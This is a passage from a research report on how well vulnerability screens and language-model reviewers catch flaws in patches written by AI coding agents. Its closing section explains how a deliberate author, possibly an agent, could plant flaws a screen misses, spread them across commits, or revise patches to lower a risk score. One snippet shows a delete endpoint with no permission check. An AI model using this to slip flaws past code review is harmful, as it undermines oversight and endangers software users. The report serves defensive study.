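Tracing known vulnerabilities back to the commits behind them gives much smaller numbers. Georgia Tech SSLab's *Vibe Security Radar* had scanned 46,831 security advisories by 24 March 2026 and linked 78 published vulnerabilities to AI-written code. It uses `git blame` to trace each fix to an earlier commit, checks that commit for an AI tool's signature, and has a language model check the result. 24% of the advisories had a fix to trace, so the 78 are about 0.7% of the traceable ones.

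That share is almost certainly too low. Hanqing Zhao, one of the tracker's researchers, told The Register that the true number was probably five to ten times as high (*Using AI to code does not mean your code is more secure*). OpenClaw, an apparently AI-written program, had more than 300 advisories, but the team could confirm AI involvement in only about 20 because most traces of it were gone. All studies that identify agents from Git records have this problem. *Debt Behind the AI Boom* (2026), for example, found commits with explicit traces of 29 AI tools in 6,699 repositories, but its method cannot detect AI code without such traces. If researchers treat unmarked agent code as human, the human baseline will include some of the agents' flaws.

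Verification latency, the delay between a flaw's introduction and its discovery, lowers these counts further because most agent code is recent. The number of AI-linked vulnerabilities rose from six in January 2026 to 35 in March, according to InfoSecurity Magazine's *Security Researchers Sound the Alarm on Vulnerabilities in AI-Generated Code*. Some of that rise may come from people finding older flaws rather than from worse code. People may also be slower to notice flaws in agent code. *Who Finishes the Job?* (2026) cites one finding that developers modify agent code less often than human code, and another that 22.7% of the issues analysers found in agents' changes were still present in the latest version.

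This evidence doesn't settle whether today's agents introduce vulnerabilities more often than people do. For routine work on established projects, a rate of around 1%, as measured by ordinary analysers, seems plausible. The rate is probably several times higher for new features that handle logins, permissions or untrusted input.

### Copying insecure code from the same project

The flaws in an agent's patch also depend on the code already in the project. In *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases*, Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026) gave agents identical tasks and changed only how secure the similar code nearby was.

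Their first experiment had 96 tasks, covering 24 small web services in each of four programming frameworks. In each task, the agent had to add one service to a project that contained no other services, up to five secure ones, or the same ones with known flaws added. The agent did not need the existing services to build the new one. The researchers tested whether each new service worked and attacked it with prepared exploits. They ran GLM 5.3, Claude Opus 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol three times on each task.

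Compared with an empty project, insecure neighbours lowered the share of services that were both correct and secure by an average of 3.4 percentage points. Secure neighbours raised it by 4.4 points, making the gap between the two conditions 7.8 points.

The second experiment used real C and C++ projects. The researchers removed code that had once contained a known memory-safety flaw, described what the code should do, and asked the agent to write it. They prepared 20 pairs of tasks. The two tasks in each pair differed in whether similar code elsewhere in the project contained the necessary safety check. A solution passed if the project compiled and did not crash on an input known to trigger the original flaw.

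In one task, the missing code had to check that some data would fit within its limits. GPT-5.6 Sol read a nearby file with similar logic, `pkcs15-myeid.c`, and included the check if and only if that file contained it.

Across five models, including Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra, secure solutions were on average 35.4 points less common when the similar code was insecure. GPT-5.6 Sol fell from 91% to 42%. Changing the prompt helped only partly:

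| Extra instruction (C and C++ tasks) | Gap between secure and insecure surroundings |
|---|---|
| None | 25 to 49 points |
| Follow the project's code style | 39 to 55 points |
| Take care not to copy bugs, or follow good security practice | 11 to 32 points |

When the researchers asked three of the agents to review their vulnerable code for bugs, the agents identified the flaw in 69.9% of cases. When asked in a separate conversation why they had written the code that way, they said in 76.5% of answers that it followed similar code elsewhere. The agents rarely warned the user without being asked. Claude Opus 5.5 did so for 11.8% of its vulnerable solutions, and GPT-6 Astra never did.

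The 35.4-point gap is between two extremes, so it does not measure how much ordinary surrounding code harms an agent's code. Sun and colleagues also chose only tasks with similar code elsewhere in the project. An automatic search found such code for 253 of 804 candidate flaws, or about a third. People also copy insecure code, and the study does not show whether agents do so more often.

If a patch copies an undiscovered flaw from existing code in the project, it will look like normal code for that project, and the model may therefore score it as less risky. Once someone has found the original flaw, a close match with it is a strong warning sign.

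### The same mistakes in unrelated projects

Agents that share a model can also repeat the same mistake across unrelated projects. *AI Code in the Wild* (Wang, Yu and colleagues, 2025) examined commits from the 1,000 most popular GitHub repositories and more than 7,000 code changes linked to published vulnerabilities. It reports that near-identical insecure templates recur across unrelated projects, and suggests that shared models spread them. It does not count the templates, so it is unclear how common they are.

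The evidence on who wrote the code is also weak. It comes from a detector that guesses from the code itself whether AI wrote it, and the detector was right 71.8% of the time. On the test data, it would have wrongly attributed about 29% of human files to AI. In the vulnerability data, it attributed less than 25% of flaws to AI, a share that could have come entirely from such errors. The differences between types of flaw are more informative. The AI share was 51% for one type involving badly escaped output and 43% for another involving weak cryptography, more than errors at the usual rate would explain.

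DryRun's small test provides clearer examples, since there was no doubt about who wrote the code. In the racing game, all three agents wrote code that accepted scores and balances from the player's computer without checking them on the server. All three also included a fixed backup secret for signing login tokens, which would let anyone who knew it forge a login. Every codebase defined a rate limiter, which stops an attacker from trying thousands of passwords, but no agent connected it to the application.

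The two sources report different results for access control, the rules on who may do what. Wang and colleagues placed only 9.6% of AI-introduced vulnerabilities in that category and 62.7% in input validation and encoding. In DryRun's test, broken access control was the most widespread problem, appearing in both applications built by each of the three agents. DryRun's agents had to build much of this protection themselves, whereas new code in an established project may be able to reuse existing access checks.

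### Which flaws a screen could learn to recognise

Flaws that involve distinctive code are the easiest for a predictor to learn. Calls to `eval()`, shell commands built from user input, weak hash functions and hardcoded passwords appear in the added lines. If many agents make the same mistake, examples from one project can help detect it in another. In one Django patch, OpenHands bypassed the framework's database tools and built an SQL command by joining strings, which made SQL injection possible. The text of that diff alone would justify a higher risk score.

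Static analysers already find many of these flaws and can identify the line responsible. A predictor trained on their findings would mostly reproduce their rules. It could add something by combining weaker signals, such as the number of files changed. In Sajadi and colleagues' data, Llama's vulnerable patches changed 1.7 files on average, compared with 1.25 for all its patches, a difference too small to be much use alone.

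Missing authorisation checks are much harder to detect. Suppose that the agent working on the picture website adds a way to delete pictures:

```
+ @app.post("/pictures/<int:id>/delete")
+ def delete_picture(id):
+     database.delete("pictures", id)
```

Suppose a coding agent adds a function that deletes a picture from a website without checking the visitor's permissions. This is safe if the website checks permissions before it runs any such function, but if each function has to make its own check, anyone can now delete anyone else's pictures. The diff is identical in both cases, so a model that reads only the diff must give both the same score. To distinguish them, it needs information about how the rest of the project handles permissions. Such flaws are also likely to be scarce in training data traced with SZZ.

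The unconnected rate limiters could be even more misleading. The diff that defines one adds sensible protective code, but the patch is flawed because no other code turns the limiter on. A model that relies on which words appear, as CodeBERT seemed to in the experiment by Nam and colleagues, might lower the score because of the new security code.

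## Adapting the screen to agent patches

The predictors described so far learned almost entirely from commits that people wrote. A project that uses one on agent patches faces *distribution shift*, a difference between the changes in the training data and those the model has to score. It can take three forms:

- In a *feature shift*, the measurements change, for instance because agents write longer messages, but a commit with given measurements is as risky as before.
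- In a *base-rate shift*, flaws become more or less common, but flawed commits still look like earlier flawed ones, and harmless commits like earlier harmless ones.
- In a *relation shift*, the same measurements indicate a different risk. A large commit by an agent might, for example, be safer than an equally large one by a person.

### Experience and ownership

Author experience changes meaning more than any other measurement when the author is an agent. The standard measures count an author's earlier changes because people learn from their work. An agent usually has little or no memory of last month's changes, and its developer can replace the underlying model while the account's change history stays the same.

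The count also depends on how the agent's commits are attributed. GitHub's Copilot agent commits under its own account, while Claude Code normally commits under the user's account and adds a "Co-Authored-By" line to the message. In the invented scoring model used earlier, the newcomer's 511-line change scored 0.82. If Copilot's account had submitted the same patch after 1,023 earlier changes, the score would have been 0.24, below the 0.70 threshold, and the patch would have passed the screen.

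A project could drop the experience measures for agent patches, or replace them with each agent version's record on each type of task. Meta's rule that each type of agent task must first go 60 days without an incident is a simple version of the second option.

The person running the agent may not know the code well either. *On Autopilot?* (Gao, Banyongrakkul et al., 2026) used `git blame` to identify who had written each project's code as it stood just before the first AI-co-authored pull request. People who had written none of that code opened 67.5% of the AI-co-authored pull requests and 61.0% of the human-only ones. The gap is small, and some of these people may have joined the project after the cut-off.

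The amount of review differed far more. Among merged pull requests from people with no prior ownership, 87% of the AI-co-authored ones had no comment or review from another person, compared with 23% of the human-only ones. Gao and colleagues suspect that the AI-co-authored pull requests were mostly easy tasks, but did not check. If a project reviews so few of these patches, a flag from the screen may be the only reason anyone reads one. The project's labels will also be less reliable, because fewer people have had a chance to notice flaws.

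### Size and spread

*Agent or Human?* (Horikawa, Li and colleagues, 2026) compared about 170,000 agent commits with 2.7 million human ones, all made in the same 1,226 projects between June 2025 and August 2026.

| Author | Commits | Median words in message | Median lines changed |
|---|---|---|---|
| People | 2,654,096 | 9 | 21 |
| Claude Code | 141,034 | 65 | 60 |
| Copilot | 27,179 | 14 | 26 |
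| Cursor | 1,160 | 36 | 41 |
| Google Jules | 313 | 56 | 36 |
| Devin | 75 | 60 | 47 |

Part of the difference in commit size arises because different projects use different agents. Within the same project, Claude Code's commits still tended to be larger, but the effect was small, and edits were spread across files in almost the same way.

*How AI Coding Agents Modify Code* (Ogenrwot and Businge, 2026) found the opposite for whole pull requests. It compared 24,014 merged agent pull requests with 5,081 human ones, and the agents' tended to be smaller. In random pairs of one human and one agent pull request, the share where the human one touched more files was 45 percentage points higher than the share where it touched fewer. For added lines, the gap was 28 points.

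The two studies measured different things. A pull request can contain many commits, and Horikawa and colleagues left out OpenAI Codex, which opened most of the agent pull requests in the dataset that Ogenrwot and Businge used. It is also unclear whether agent or human pull requests contain more commits. Ogenrwot and Businge report that human ones do, but their totals average 18 commits per agent pull request and fewer than five per human one. A few agent pull requests with very many commits could explain the discrepancy.

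A screen that scores commits could therefore rate agents' work as riskier because of its size, while one that scores pull requests could rate it as safer. In the invented scoring model, going from 21 changed lines to 60, if all were additions, would raise the predicted odds of a flaw by about 80%. That increase is justified only if size still indicates risk. Size may be a weaker sign of risk for agents, which can produce 500 lines of routine code in one go, than for people, who have many chances to lose track of something while writing that much. The number of files changed probably remains somewhat useful, since Llama's vulnerable patches in the study by Sajadi and colleagues changed more files than its average patch.

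### Messages

Messages differ more between agents and people than any other feature does. In the typical project that Horikawa and colleagues studied, the median message had 73 words for Claude Code and 10 for people. Ogenrwot and Businge used two language models to measure how closely each description resembled its diff. Agents' descriptions scored slightly higher on average than people's, and their scores varied less.

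A predictor that uses commit messages loses a useful clue when an agent writes them. A vague or hurried message from a person may indicate hurried work, but an agent writes a fluent message whether or not its code is sound.

Long messages can also distort the bug-fix measure, FIX, which often depends on keywords. Suppose each word in a message has a 1% chance of being "fix", "bug" or something similar. A 10-word message would contain at least one such word about 10% of the time, and a 73-word message about 52% of the time. The screen would treat many ordinary agent commits as bug fixes and raise their scores.

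People's commits are changing too. Between 2020–21 and 2025–26, the median human commit message in these projects grew from seven words to nine, and the median change grew from 16 lines to 21. Some of these commits probably include unlabelled AI work. A predictor trained on old human commits would therefore need updating even in a project that banned agents.

### Recognising agent commits

A screen must identify agent patches before it can treat them differently. Signatures are unreliable because users can remove them. Claude Code lets users replace its attribution with any text, and Cursor lets them turn it off. Horikawa and colleagues stripped out the signatures and tested whether a classifier could still recognise agent commits.

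Their best classifier, which weighs the words in the commit message and the diff, had a ROC-AUC of 0.859. Agents wrote 5.9% of the test commits. The classifier flagged half of these, but two thirds of the commits it flagged were by humans, so a screen that used it to identify agent patches would mostly select human ones.

Most of the signal came from the message and the size of the change. With the diff alone, ROC-AUC fell to 0.716. Among commits of similar size from the same project, language and month, it fell to 0.53 for Claude Code and 0.55 for Copilot, close to chance. This is mildly encouraging for predictors such as CodeJIT that use only the code, because their inputs have apparently shifted less. The result doesn't show that the code is equally safe, since similar-looking sets of changes can contain different numbers of flaws.

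The classifier also failed on agents missing from its training data. When the researchers left out Claude Code, ROC-AUC for Claude Code commits was 0.524. Even for an agent included in training, results varied from month to month. A simpler classifier trained on data from June 2025 had a ROC-AUC of 0.83 for Copilot in July 2025, 0.61 in May 2026 and 0.78 in August 2026. The dip roughly coincided with a fall in the share of Copilot messages containing a standard "Initial plan" line.

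Projects that want to treat agent patches separately would do better to require disclosure at commit time. Horikawa and colleagues suggest that agent developers record authorship in signed data that survives later edits.

### Correcting for a different base rate

A pure base-rate shift is easy to correct with a more general form of the formula given earlier for models trained on balanced data. Suppose that a screen's scores are accurate probabilities for human commits, with base rate *b*₀, and that agent patches have base rate *b*₁. If the screen gives an agent patch probability *p*, the corrected probability *p*′ satisfies

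*p*′ / (1 − *p*′) = *p* / (1 − *p*) × [*b*₁ / (1 − *b*₁)] / [*b*₀ / (1 − *b*₀)]

The table applies this to a human base rate of 0.5%. It includes both a lower and a higher rate for agents because the evidence is not sufficient to tell which is right.

| Screen's estimate | Corrected, if 0.25% of agent patches are flawed | Corrected, if 2% are flawed |
|---|---|---|
| 0.5% | 0.25% | 2.0% |
| 1% | 0.5% | 3.9% |
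| 5% | 2.6% | 18% |
| 20% | 11% | 50% |

A team that reviews anything with at least a 2% risk would have to review every agent patch rated at 0.5% or more by the screen in the last column's case, but only those rated at about 3.9% or more in the middle column's. The correction does not change the ranking of agent patches, so it cannot help reviewers who read a fixed number of them find more flaws. In a queue that also contains human commits, it moves all the agent patches up or down together relative to the human commits.

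The base rate can strongly affect precision, as shown by a classifier that Horikawa and colleagues trained on data from June 2025 to detect agent commits rather than vulnerabilities. Its precision for Claude Code rose from 2.8% to 32.0% as Claude Code's share of the test commits grew from 0.3% to 10.8%. Its ROC-AUC stayed between 0.67 and 0.78, so it had not become much better at distinguishing Claude Code's commits from others.

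It is tempting to estimate the new base rate from the number of alarms. If a screen has recall *r* and false-alarm rate *f*, the share of patches it flags is *g* = *br* + (1 − *b*)*f*, so

*b* = (*g* − *f*) / (*r* − *f*)

If a screen with 80% recall and a 10% false-alarm rate flags 11.4% of agent patches, the implied base rate is 2%. This estimate is reliable only if there is no feature shift. Suppose the true base rate is still 0.5%, but agents' larger commits have doubled the false-alarm rate to 20%. The screen would then flag 20.3% of patches, and the formula, still assuming a 10% false-alarm rate, would give a base rate of about 15%, roughly 30 times too high.

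### Why only fresh labels reveal a relation shift

A project can detect a feature shift by comparing measurements, but not a relation shift, which changes neither the measurements nor the scores. In the invented example below, a screen checks 1,000 agent patches, 400 large and 600 small, and flags every large one.

| | Flaws in large patches | Flaws in small patches | Total flaws | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
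| Size indicates risk, as in human commits | 8 | 3 | 11 | 73% |
| Size no longer indicates risk | 2 | 9 | 11 | 18% |

Both rows have the same patches, scores, number of alarms and base rate, so the only way to tell which row describes the project is to find out which patches are flawed.

Vulnerability reports arrive too slowly to be used for adapting the screen. In the Linux data described earlier, developers fixed only about a third of the flaws within a year, and by then most teams will be using a different version of the agent. Hesamolhokama and colleagues describe the same difficulty with ordinary bugs, where labels arrive late and the proportion of buggy commits changes in the meantime. It is faster to have security reviewers examine a sample of recent agent patches. The sample needs to include patches that the screen passed, because reviewers who see only flagged patches can't find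 the flaws it misses.

None of the studies described here tests a vulnerability predictor trained on human commits on agent commits. To do so, researchers could train the predictor on human commits up to a certain date, fix the threshold, and then run it on later human and agent commits from the same projects. Reviewers who do not know the author or the score would label both groups by the same procedure. Comparing ROC-AUC between the groups would show whether the predictor ranks agent commits as well as human ones, and comparing recall at the fixed threshold would show whether it catches as large a share of the vulnerable ones. Retraining the predictor on agent commits would show how much of any lost performance new data could recover.

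Such tests are probably scarce because labelling takes so much work. If 1% of agent patches are flawed, reviewers would have to read 10,000 to find about 100 flaws, and a measured recall of 60% would still have a margin of error of about 10 percentage points. Sampling high-scoring patches more heavily, then correcting the estimate for this, would reduce the work.

### Predicting which agent pull requests will be costly

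The closest evidence comes from a model that predicts review effort rather than flaws. Dao, Pham and colleagues (2026), in *Early-Stage Prediction of Review Effort in AI-Generated Pull Requests*, trained it on part of a set of 33,707 agent pull requests, using information available when the agent opened each one. They counted a pull request as high-effort if it ranked in the top fifth by number of reviews and comments.

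On later pull requests, the model had a ROC-AUC of 0.96, and the 20% it ranked highest contained 69% of those that required high review effort. On projects outside its training data, its ROC-AUC was 0.83. A model that used only the number of changed lines did almost as well on later pull requests, at 0.93, but fell to 0.65 on new projects. Size evidently predicts review effort much better when the model has been trained on pull requests from the same project.

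This shows that simple measurements of agent patches can predict something useful, at least when the training data also comes from agents. But it provides little evidence that they can predict vulnerabilities, because a pull request merged without comment counts as needing little review even if it contains a serious flaw. Most AI-co-authored pull requests in Gao and colleagues' data had no comments from other people.

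### What a language-model reviewer reads

A language-model reviewer reads the change and writes a description of any suspected flaws. It can open other files, so it could check whether code elsewhere in a website verifies permissions before a new delete function runs. Unlike a risk score, its report can also include the faulty line and how an attacker could exploit it.

Judging a patch often requires looking at other files. *Benchmarking LLMs and LLM-based Agents in Practical Vulnerability Detection for Code Repositories*, by Yildiz, Teo and colleagues, cites an estimate that 24.3% of vulnerabilities in real C and C++ projects involve more than one function, with function calls an average of 2.8 levels deep.

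The JITVUL benchmark contains 879 published vulnerabilities of 91 types. Each vulnerability provides two tests. The first contains the function and its project when the function became vulnerable, and the second contains both after the fix. A model has to label the function vulnerable in the first test and safe in the second. This is a strict test of understanding because the two versions often differ by only a line or two.

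The researchers tested two OpenAI models, GPT-4o-mini and GPT-4o, in three arrangements. The results below are for a basic prompt.

| What the model receives | GPT-4o-mini: F1 | GPT-4o-mini: pairs correct | GPT-4o: F1 | GPT-4o: pairs correct |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The function only | 0.56 | 3.4% | 0.66 | 1.0% |
| The function and up to ten related ones | 0.53 | 2.1% | 0.63 | 1.0% |
| The function and tools for looking up others | 0.57 | 12.6% | 0.58 | 17.6% |

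The F1 scores are misleading. Labelling every function vulnerable would have scored 0.67, more than either model achieved with any prompt, and GPT-4o without tools labelled nearly every function that way. Better prompts raised the share of pairs with both functions labelled correctly to at most 20.2%, below the 25% expected from tossing a coin for each function.

On a more realistic set of 695 vulnerable functions and 25,216 safe ones, GPT-4o-mini's F1 was between 0.05 and 0.12, depending on the prompt, compared with 0.05 for labeling every function vulnerable.

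JITVUL also uses a different version of the code than a real merge check would. Yildiz and colleagues treated the last commit that changed the function before the fix as the one that introduced the flaw, although the flaw may be older. The models therefore saw the code as it stood just before the fix. The detector LineVul found far more flaws in that version than in the code as it stood when the flaws were introduced, though language models may not have the same weakness.

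Both models are well out of date, so these results are mainly of historical interest. The 2026 system by Chen and colleagues, described earlier, flagged vulnerability-introducing commits far more often than fixes, so it did at least distinguish between them. Finding bugs with no hint of where to look is still hard. *Do Coding Agents Catch Their Own Bugs?* (Patel, Liao and colleagues, 2026) cites two 2026 benchmarks that ask agents to find and repair bugs in a whole project without a bug report. The best agents repaired 20.0% of the bugs in one and 9.5% in the other.

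### Whether agents catch their own bugs

Patel and colleagues tested whether agents avoid introducing bugs. They collected 212 pairs of pull requests in which the second fixed a bug that the first had introduced. In one pair, a developer changed how Pytest, a Python testing tool, recognises the folders where Python keeps installed packages. The change passed review, but 23 days later users reported that Pytest had started running tests from packages installed with another popular tool. The pairs cover bugs of all kinds, and only some are vulnerabilities.

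Eleven models each received the first task with no mention of the later defect. On average, they completed the task in 60.7% of cases, but in only 14.8% did they also avoid the defect. When the researchers described the defect to five of the models, those models repaired it 91.2% of the time, so the difficulty was mostly in noticing it.

The benchmark includes only defects that a human developer introduced and other people failed to notice, half of them for 88 days or more. The original developers would therefore score zero, so agents' results on it do not show that they are worse than people.

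The researchers then asked three of the models to review and repair their own finished patches, using the review commands built into Claude Code and Codex.

| Model | Completed the task: before → after review | Also avoided the defect: before → after review |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 84.4% → 69.8% | 18.4% → 24.1% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 77.8% → 68.4% | 24.5% → 35.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 59.9% → 57.1% | 17.0% → 18.4% |

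Self-review helped all three models avoid more defects, but it also broke some working patches. Asking GPT-5.6 Sol at the start to think about unstated edge cases worked better than self-review. It then avoided the defect in 31.6% of cases and still completed 82.5% of the tasks. The same request lowered both rates for Claude Sonnet 5.

A project could limit the damage by having the reviewer report problems without changing the code, or by rerunning all the tests after every repair. Each repair also needs a new security check. In Surikov's (2026) *Securing AI-Generated Code*, Claude models wrote short Python programs and then rewrote them in response to reported flaws. Depending on the model and the information it received, 15% to 22% of the rewrites introduced at least one type of flaw that static analysers had not found in the original.

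### Checks that GitHub and Anthropic offered by December 2026

By December 2026, developers could add a language-model reviewer to a project by changing a setting. GitHub's checks start before the pull request exists. *GitHub scans the code your pull request never touched* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports that Copilot's coding agent has used CodeQL, GitHub's static analyser, to scan its own code since October 2025. The agent also checks for exposed passwords and for known vulnerabilities in outside packages it adds. If it finds a problem, it tries to fix it and reports this in the pull request.

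GitHub's *Code scanning shows AI security detections on pull requests* (2026) announced a language-model check that runs on the pull request itself. The check examines languages that CodeQL doesn't cover, such as PHP and shell scripts, and can search the rest of the project before reporting a flaw. According to the product's documentation, *AI Scan for pull requests*, the check's findings are advisory and cannot block a merge. The check also skips pull requests from forks, the separate copies of a project in which outsiders usually prepare their changes, so it does not cover most patches that outsiders submit to a public project.

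Anthropic's *Automate security reviews with Claude Code* describes the company's similar tool, which reviews each new pull request and comments on suspect lines. Anthropic's *Claude Security* describes a newer product that first scans a whole branch of a project, using its Git history and the flow of data through the code. It then scans later changes according to their risk and complexity. *Claude Security can now spot vulnerabilities that reappear in code* (Pogorelec, 2026) reported in October that an update had added recurring scans and automatic tracking of fixes. *When AI Writes the Code, Anthropic Wants AI Guarding the Merge* (Smith, 2026) reported that Anthropic had also connected the product to pull requests on GitHub by 2 December.

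A commit-level screen selects changes by risk, so the two methods can work together. A cheap predictor scores every commit, and a more expensive reviewer reads only the ones that score highest. The drawback is that a flawed commit gets through if either one misses it. If the screen sends 60% of the flawed commits to the reviewer and the reviewer recognises 70% of those, together they catch 42%.

It is hard to tell how well the commercial tools work. GitHub warns of false positives in its documentation but gives no rate. The company reports that it detected more than 200 million vulnerabilities between January and October 2026, but that total doesn't measure accuracy because it leaves out false alarms and missed flaws.

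### Why an author and a reviewer may miss the same flaws

A reviewer built on the same model as the author may be worst at finding the flaws that the author leaves behind. Suppose a model detects 90% of familiar flaws and 20% of unfamiliar ones, both when writing and when reviewing, and a task offers 100 chances to make each kind.

| Kind of flaw | Chances | Left in the code by the author | Caught by the same model as reviewer |
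|---|---|---|---|
| Familiar | 100 | 10 | 9 |
| Unfamiliar | 100 | 80 | 16 |
| Total | 200 | 90 | 25 |

This reviewer would catch 55% of flaws in code where half are easy for its model to recognise and half are hard. In code written by the same model, it would catch 25 of 90, or 28%, because the model has already avoided most of the flaws it finds easy to recognise. Recall measured on human code could therefore greatly overstate recall on agent patches.

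The example assumes that an agent avoids every flaw it can recognise, but real agents do not. In the study by Sun and colleagues, agents could usually identify the flaws in their own code when asked to review it, even though they had not avoided them while writing. A separate review by the same model can catch many of these mistakes. Patel and colleagues also found some benefit from self-review, but neither study compared self-review with a review of the same patches by a different model.

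Using another company's model may help less than it seems, since the leading models probably learned from much of the same public code. Patel and colleagues describe a task on which all eleven models, from five developers, made the same mistake. Their code read a stream of values twice, but Python lets a program read that kind of stream only once. The human repair changed one line. This one case is weak evidence of a shared blind spot, because at the models' measured success rates, all eleven would have failed about 35 of the 212 tasks even if their failures had been unrelated.

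A static analyser is a better candidate for an independent check because it applies fixed rules and tends to make different mistakes. In Surikov's experiment, feedback from a Claude reviewer reduced the number of flaws that two analysers detected by 42% on average. Adding the analysers' own findings to the feedback increased the reduction to 57%. Some of that gain was inevitable because Surikov used the same analysers to measure the result. Still, the addition helped all four models tested, which suggests that the Claude reviewer had missed or failed to explain some flaws that simple rules could find.

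## Why the statistics stop applying when a flaw is deliberate

The recall figures so far describe flaws that people and agents presumably introduced by accident. They do not establish a minimum rate at which the same screen would catch flaws that somebody inserted on purpose.

Security researchers have long treated accidental and deliberate flaws differently. In *A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws, with Examples*, Landwehr, Bull and colleagues (1994) sorted 50 documented flaws partly by whether someone had introduced them intentionally. They argued that if most flaws are accidental, spending more on code review and testing may work reasonably well. If most of the serious ones are malicious, those measures are "much less likely to help", and it may be better to hire more trustworthy programmers or pay experts to attack the software. They offered no measurements to support this.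 A screen that learns from past flaws is also less likely to help against malicious ones, partly for statistical reasons.

### Recall as an average

Let *P*(*x*) be the probability that a randomly chosen flawed change is *x*, and let *f*(*x*) be 1 if the screen flags *x* and 0 if it passes it. Recall is

*r* = Σ *P*(*x*) *f*(*x*)

where the sum covers every possible flawed change. The screen determines *f*, but *P* depends on how flaws come about. Researchers estimate *r* by running the screen on known flawed commits, which they treat as a sample from *P*.

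In the invented example below, accidental flaws come in three kinds.

| Kind of flaw | Share of accidental flaws | Share that the screen flags |
|---|---|---|
| A | 60% | 95% |
| B | 30% | 70% |
| C | 10% | 20% |

Recall is 0.57 + 0.21 + 0.02, or 80%. The same screen has a recall of only 20% for an author who introduces only flaws of kind C. If the author picks a flaw from the four fifths of kind C that the screen misses, recall is zero.

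A deliberate author replaces *P* with another distribution, *Q*, and recall becomes Σ *Q*(*x*) *f*(*x*). This sum can take any value from 0 to 1 if the screen flags some flawed changes and passes others. A measured recall of 80% means that the screen misses 20% of accidental flaws, but a deliberate author needs only one of the changes it misses.

The shift from human accidents to agent accidents is less serious, provided it is limited. If no flawed change is more than *c* times as common in use as it was in testing, the miss rate is at most *c*(1 − *r*), where *r* is the recall measured in testing. With 80% recall and *c* = 2, the screen would miss at most 40% of flaws. At *c* = 5 the limit is 100%, so the screen could miss every flaw. A deliberate author may choose a change that almost never happens by accident, so *c* can be arbitrarily large.

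If a project closely reviews a random 5% of unflagged changes, chosen after the author submits them, every deliberate flaw is guaranteed at least a 5% chance of close review, no matter which change the author puts it in.

### Spam filters and school admissions

Researchers first studied this problem in spam filtering. *Adversarial Classification* (Dalvi, Domingos and colleagues, 2004) models it as a game in which a filter learns from old mail and a spammer then alters new messages to get them through, with a penalty for the changes. The spammer can change only spam, not legitimate mail, so the filter's recall can collapse while its false-alarm rate stays the same.

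The same would happen with code. The hypothetical screen at the start flagged 500 of 10,000 changes. If someone added five deliberate flaws, it would flag between 500 and 505, and a team that watched the number of alarms would not notice them.

Dalvi and colleagues tested an ordinary spam filter on 481 spam messages and 2,412 legitimate ones. Their simulated spammers knew exactly how the filter worked and could make up to about 20 small changes to each message. The researchers also built a second filter that anticipated the changes.

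| Spam messages | Missed by the ordinary filter | Missed by the anticipating filter |
|---|---|---|
| Unaltered | 94 | not applicable |
| Altered by adding words | 481 | 93 |
| Altered only by swapping in synonyms | 408 | 164 |

In the second row, the ordinary filter's recall fell from 80% to zero when the spammers altered their messages, while the number of legitimate messages it wrongly blocked stayed at two. The anticipating filter recovered all of that loss, but under favourable conditions. It was given the penalty the spammers incurred for each alteration, and the spammers assumed that they still faced the ordinary filter. When both sides could keep responding to each other, the filter's performance swung between two levels without settling.

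Dalvi and colleagues note that methods for handling gradual drift in the data do not solve the problem, because they do not allow for changes that depend on the classifier itself. Frequent retraining helps a spam filter partly because people report spam quickly. A vulnerability may take years to be found, so a screen might be retrained only on flaws an opponent planted years earlier, or on none of them.

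Hardt, Megiddo and colleagues (2015), in *Strategic Classification*, gave the problem a more general form. Their opening example is a school that admits children partly by the number of books at home, which goes with success at school. Once parents know this, they can buy an attic full of books that nobody reads. In the formal game, a player called Jury publishes a classifier *f* that returns +1 (accept) or −1 (reject). A second player, Contestant, has features *x* and changes them to

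Δ(*x*) = argmax over *y* of [*f*(*y*) − *c*(*x*, *y*)]

where *c*(*x*, *y*) is the cost of changing *x* into *y*. Acceptance is worth 2 more than rejection, so a rejected Contestant changes *x* whenever some acceptable *y* costs less than 2. Jury wants *f*(Δ(*x*)) to match the true label of the original *x* as often as possible.

For a code screen, *x* is a flawed change and *y* is a version that passes and still serves the author's purpose. Hardt and colleagues found an efficient way to get close to the best possible classifier when each version can be assigned a number and the effort of changing one version into another is the difference between their numbers. They also proved that, for effort in general, getting very close to the best classifier is NP-hard, so an efficient method almost certainly doesn't exist.

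Even the best possible classifier may perform poorly. If an agent can easily rewrite nearly every flawed change so that it passes, the most accurate screen might flag nothing.

### Five assumptions behind a recall figure

A project that applies a measured recall to new changes has to make several assumptions, and accidental and deliberate flaws meet them to different degrees.

| Assumption | Accidental flaws in agent patches | Deliberate flaws |
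|---|---|---|
| The same process produces flaws in the training data and in use | Roughly at best, since agents' changes differ from people's | No |
| The author does not choose a version in view of the score | Usually, unless an agent revises its patch until it passes | Only if the author cannot learn or estimate the score |
| Each flaw lies within one scored change | Often, but some depend on code elsewhere | Only if the author happens to work that way |
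| The labels include flaws of this kind | In part, since undiscovered and unfixed flaws are missing | Hardly at all |
| Misses are not systematic | No, but nobody is taking advantage of the pattern | No, and an author may take advantage of it |

*BugPilot* (Sonwane, White and colleagues, 2025) shows that the same author can produce bugs through two very different processes. The researchers wanted realistic bugs for training coding agents. In one arrangement, they told an agent running on Claude Sonnet 4 to insert a bug. In the other, they told it to add a feature without breaking anything, and kept the results that broke an existing test.

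| Average per bug | Inserted on purpose | Introduced while adding a feature |
|---|---|---|
| Length of the diff in tokens | 435 | 4,376 |
| Files changed | 1.3 | 4.2 |
| Net lines added | 12 | 416 |
| Repaired by Claude Sonnet 4 | 54.6% | 41.4% |

A screen that gives weight to size would treat these two groups very differently. The deliberate bugs were also concentrated in a few categories, though the instructions had suggested some of them. The comparison exaggerates the gap to expect in a real project, because the agent that inserted bugs had no other work to do, while a real saboteur would normally hide a flaw in a useful patch. The bugs were also ordinary ones, not vulnerabilities.

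A screen's measured recall applies only if authors don't use its risk score to choose which version of a patch to submit. Even an honest author can break this condition. GitHub's coding agent already revises its patches in response to static-analysis findings. If an agent did the same with a risk score, some revisions would remove the flaw and others would only lower the score. The remaining flaws would be accidental but harder for the screen to detect, so it would catch a smaller share of them than its measured recall.

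Datasets attach each label to a single commit, so recall is calculated per commit. This works for an accidental flaw such as the path traversal in the picture website, but less well for the unprotected delete function, where the danger depends on code that the commit didn't touch. Someone who adds a flaw deliberately can spread it across several commits.

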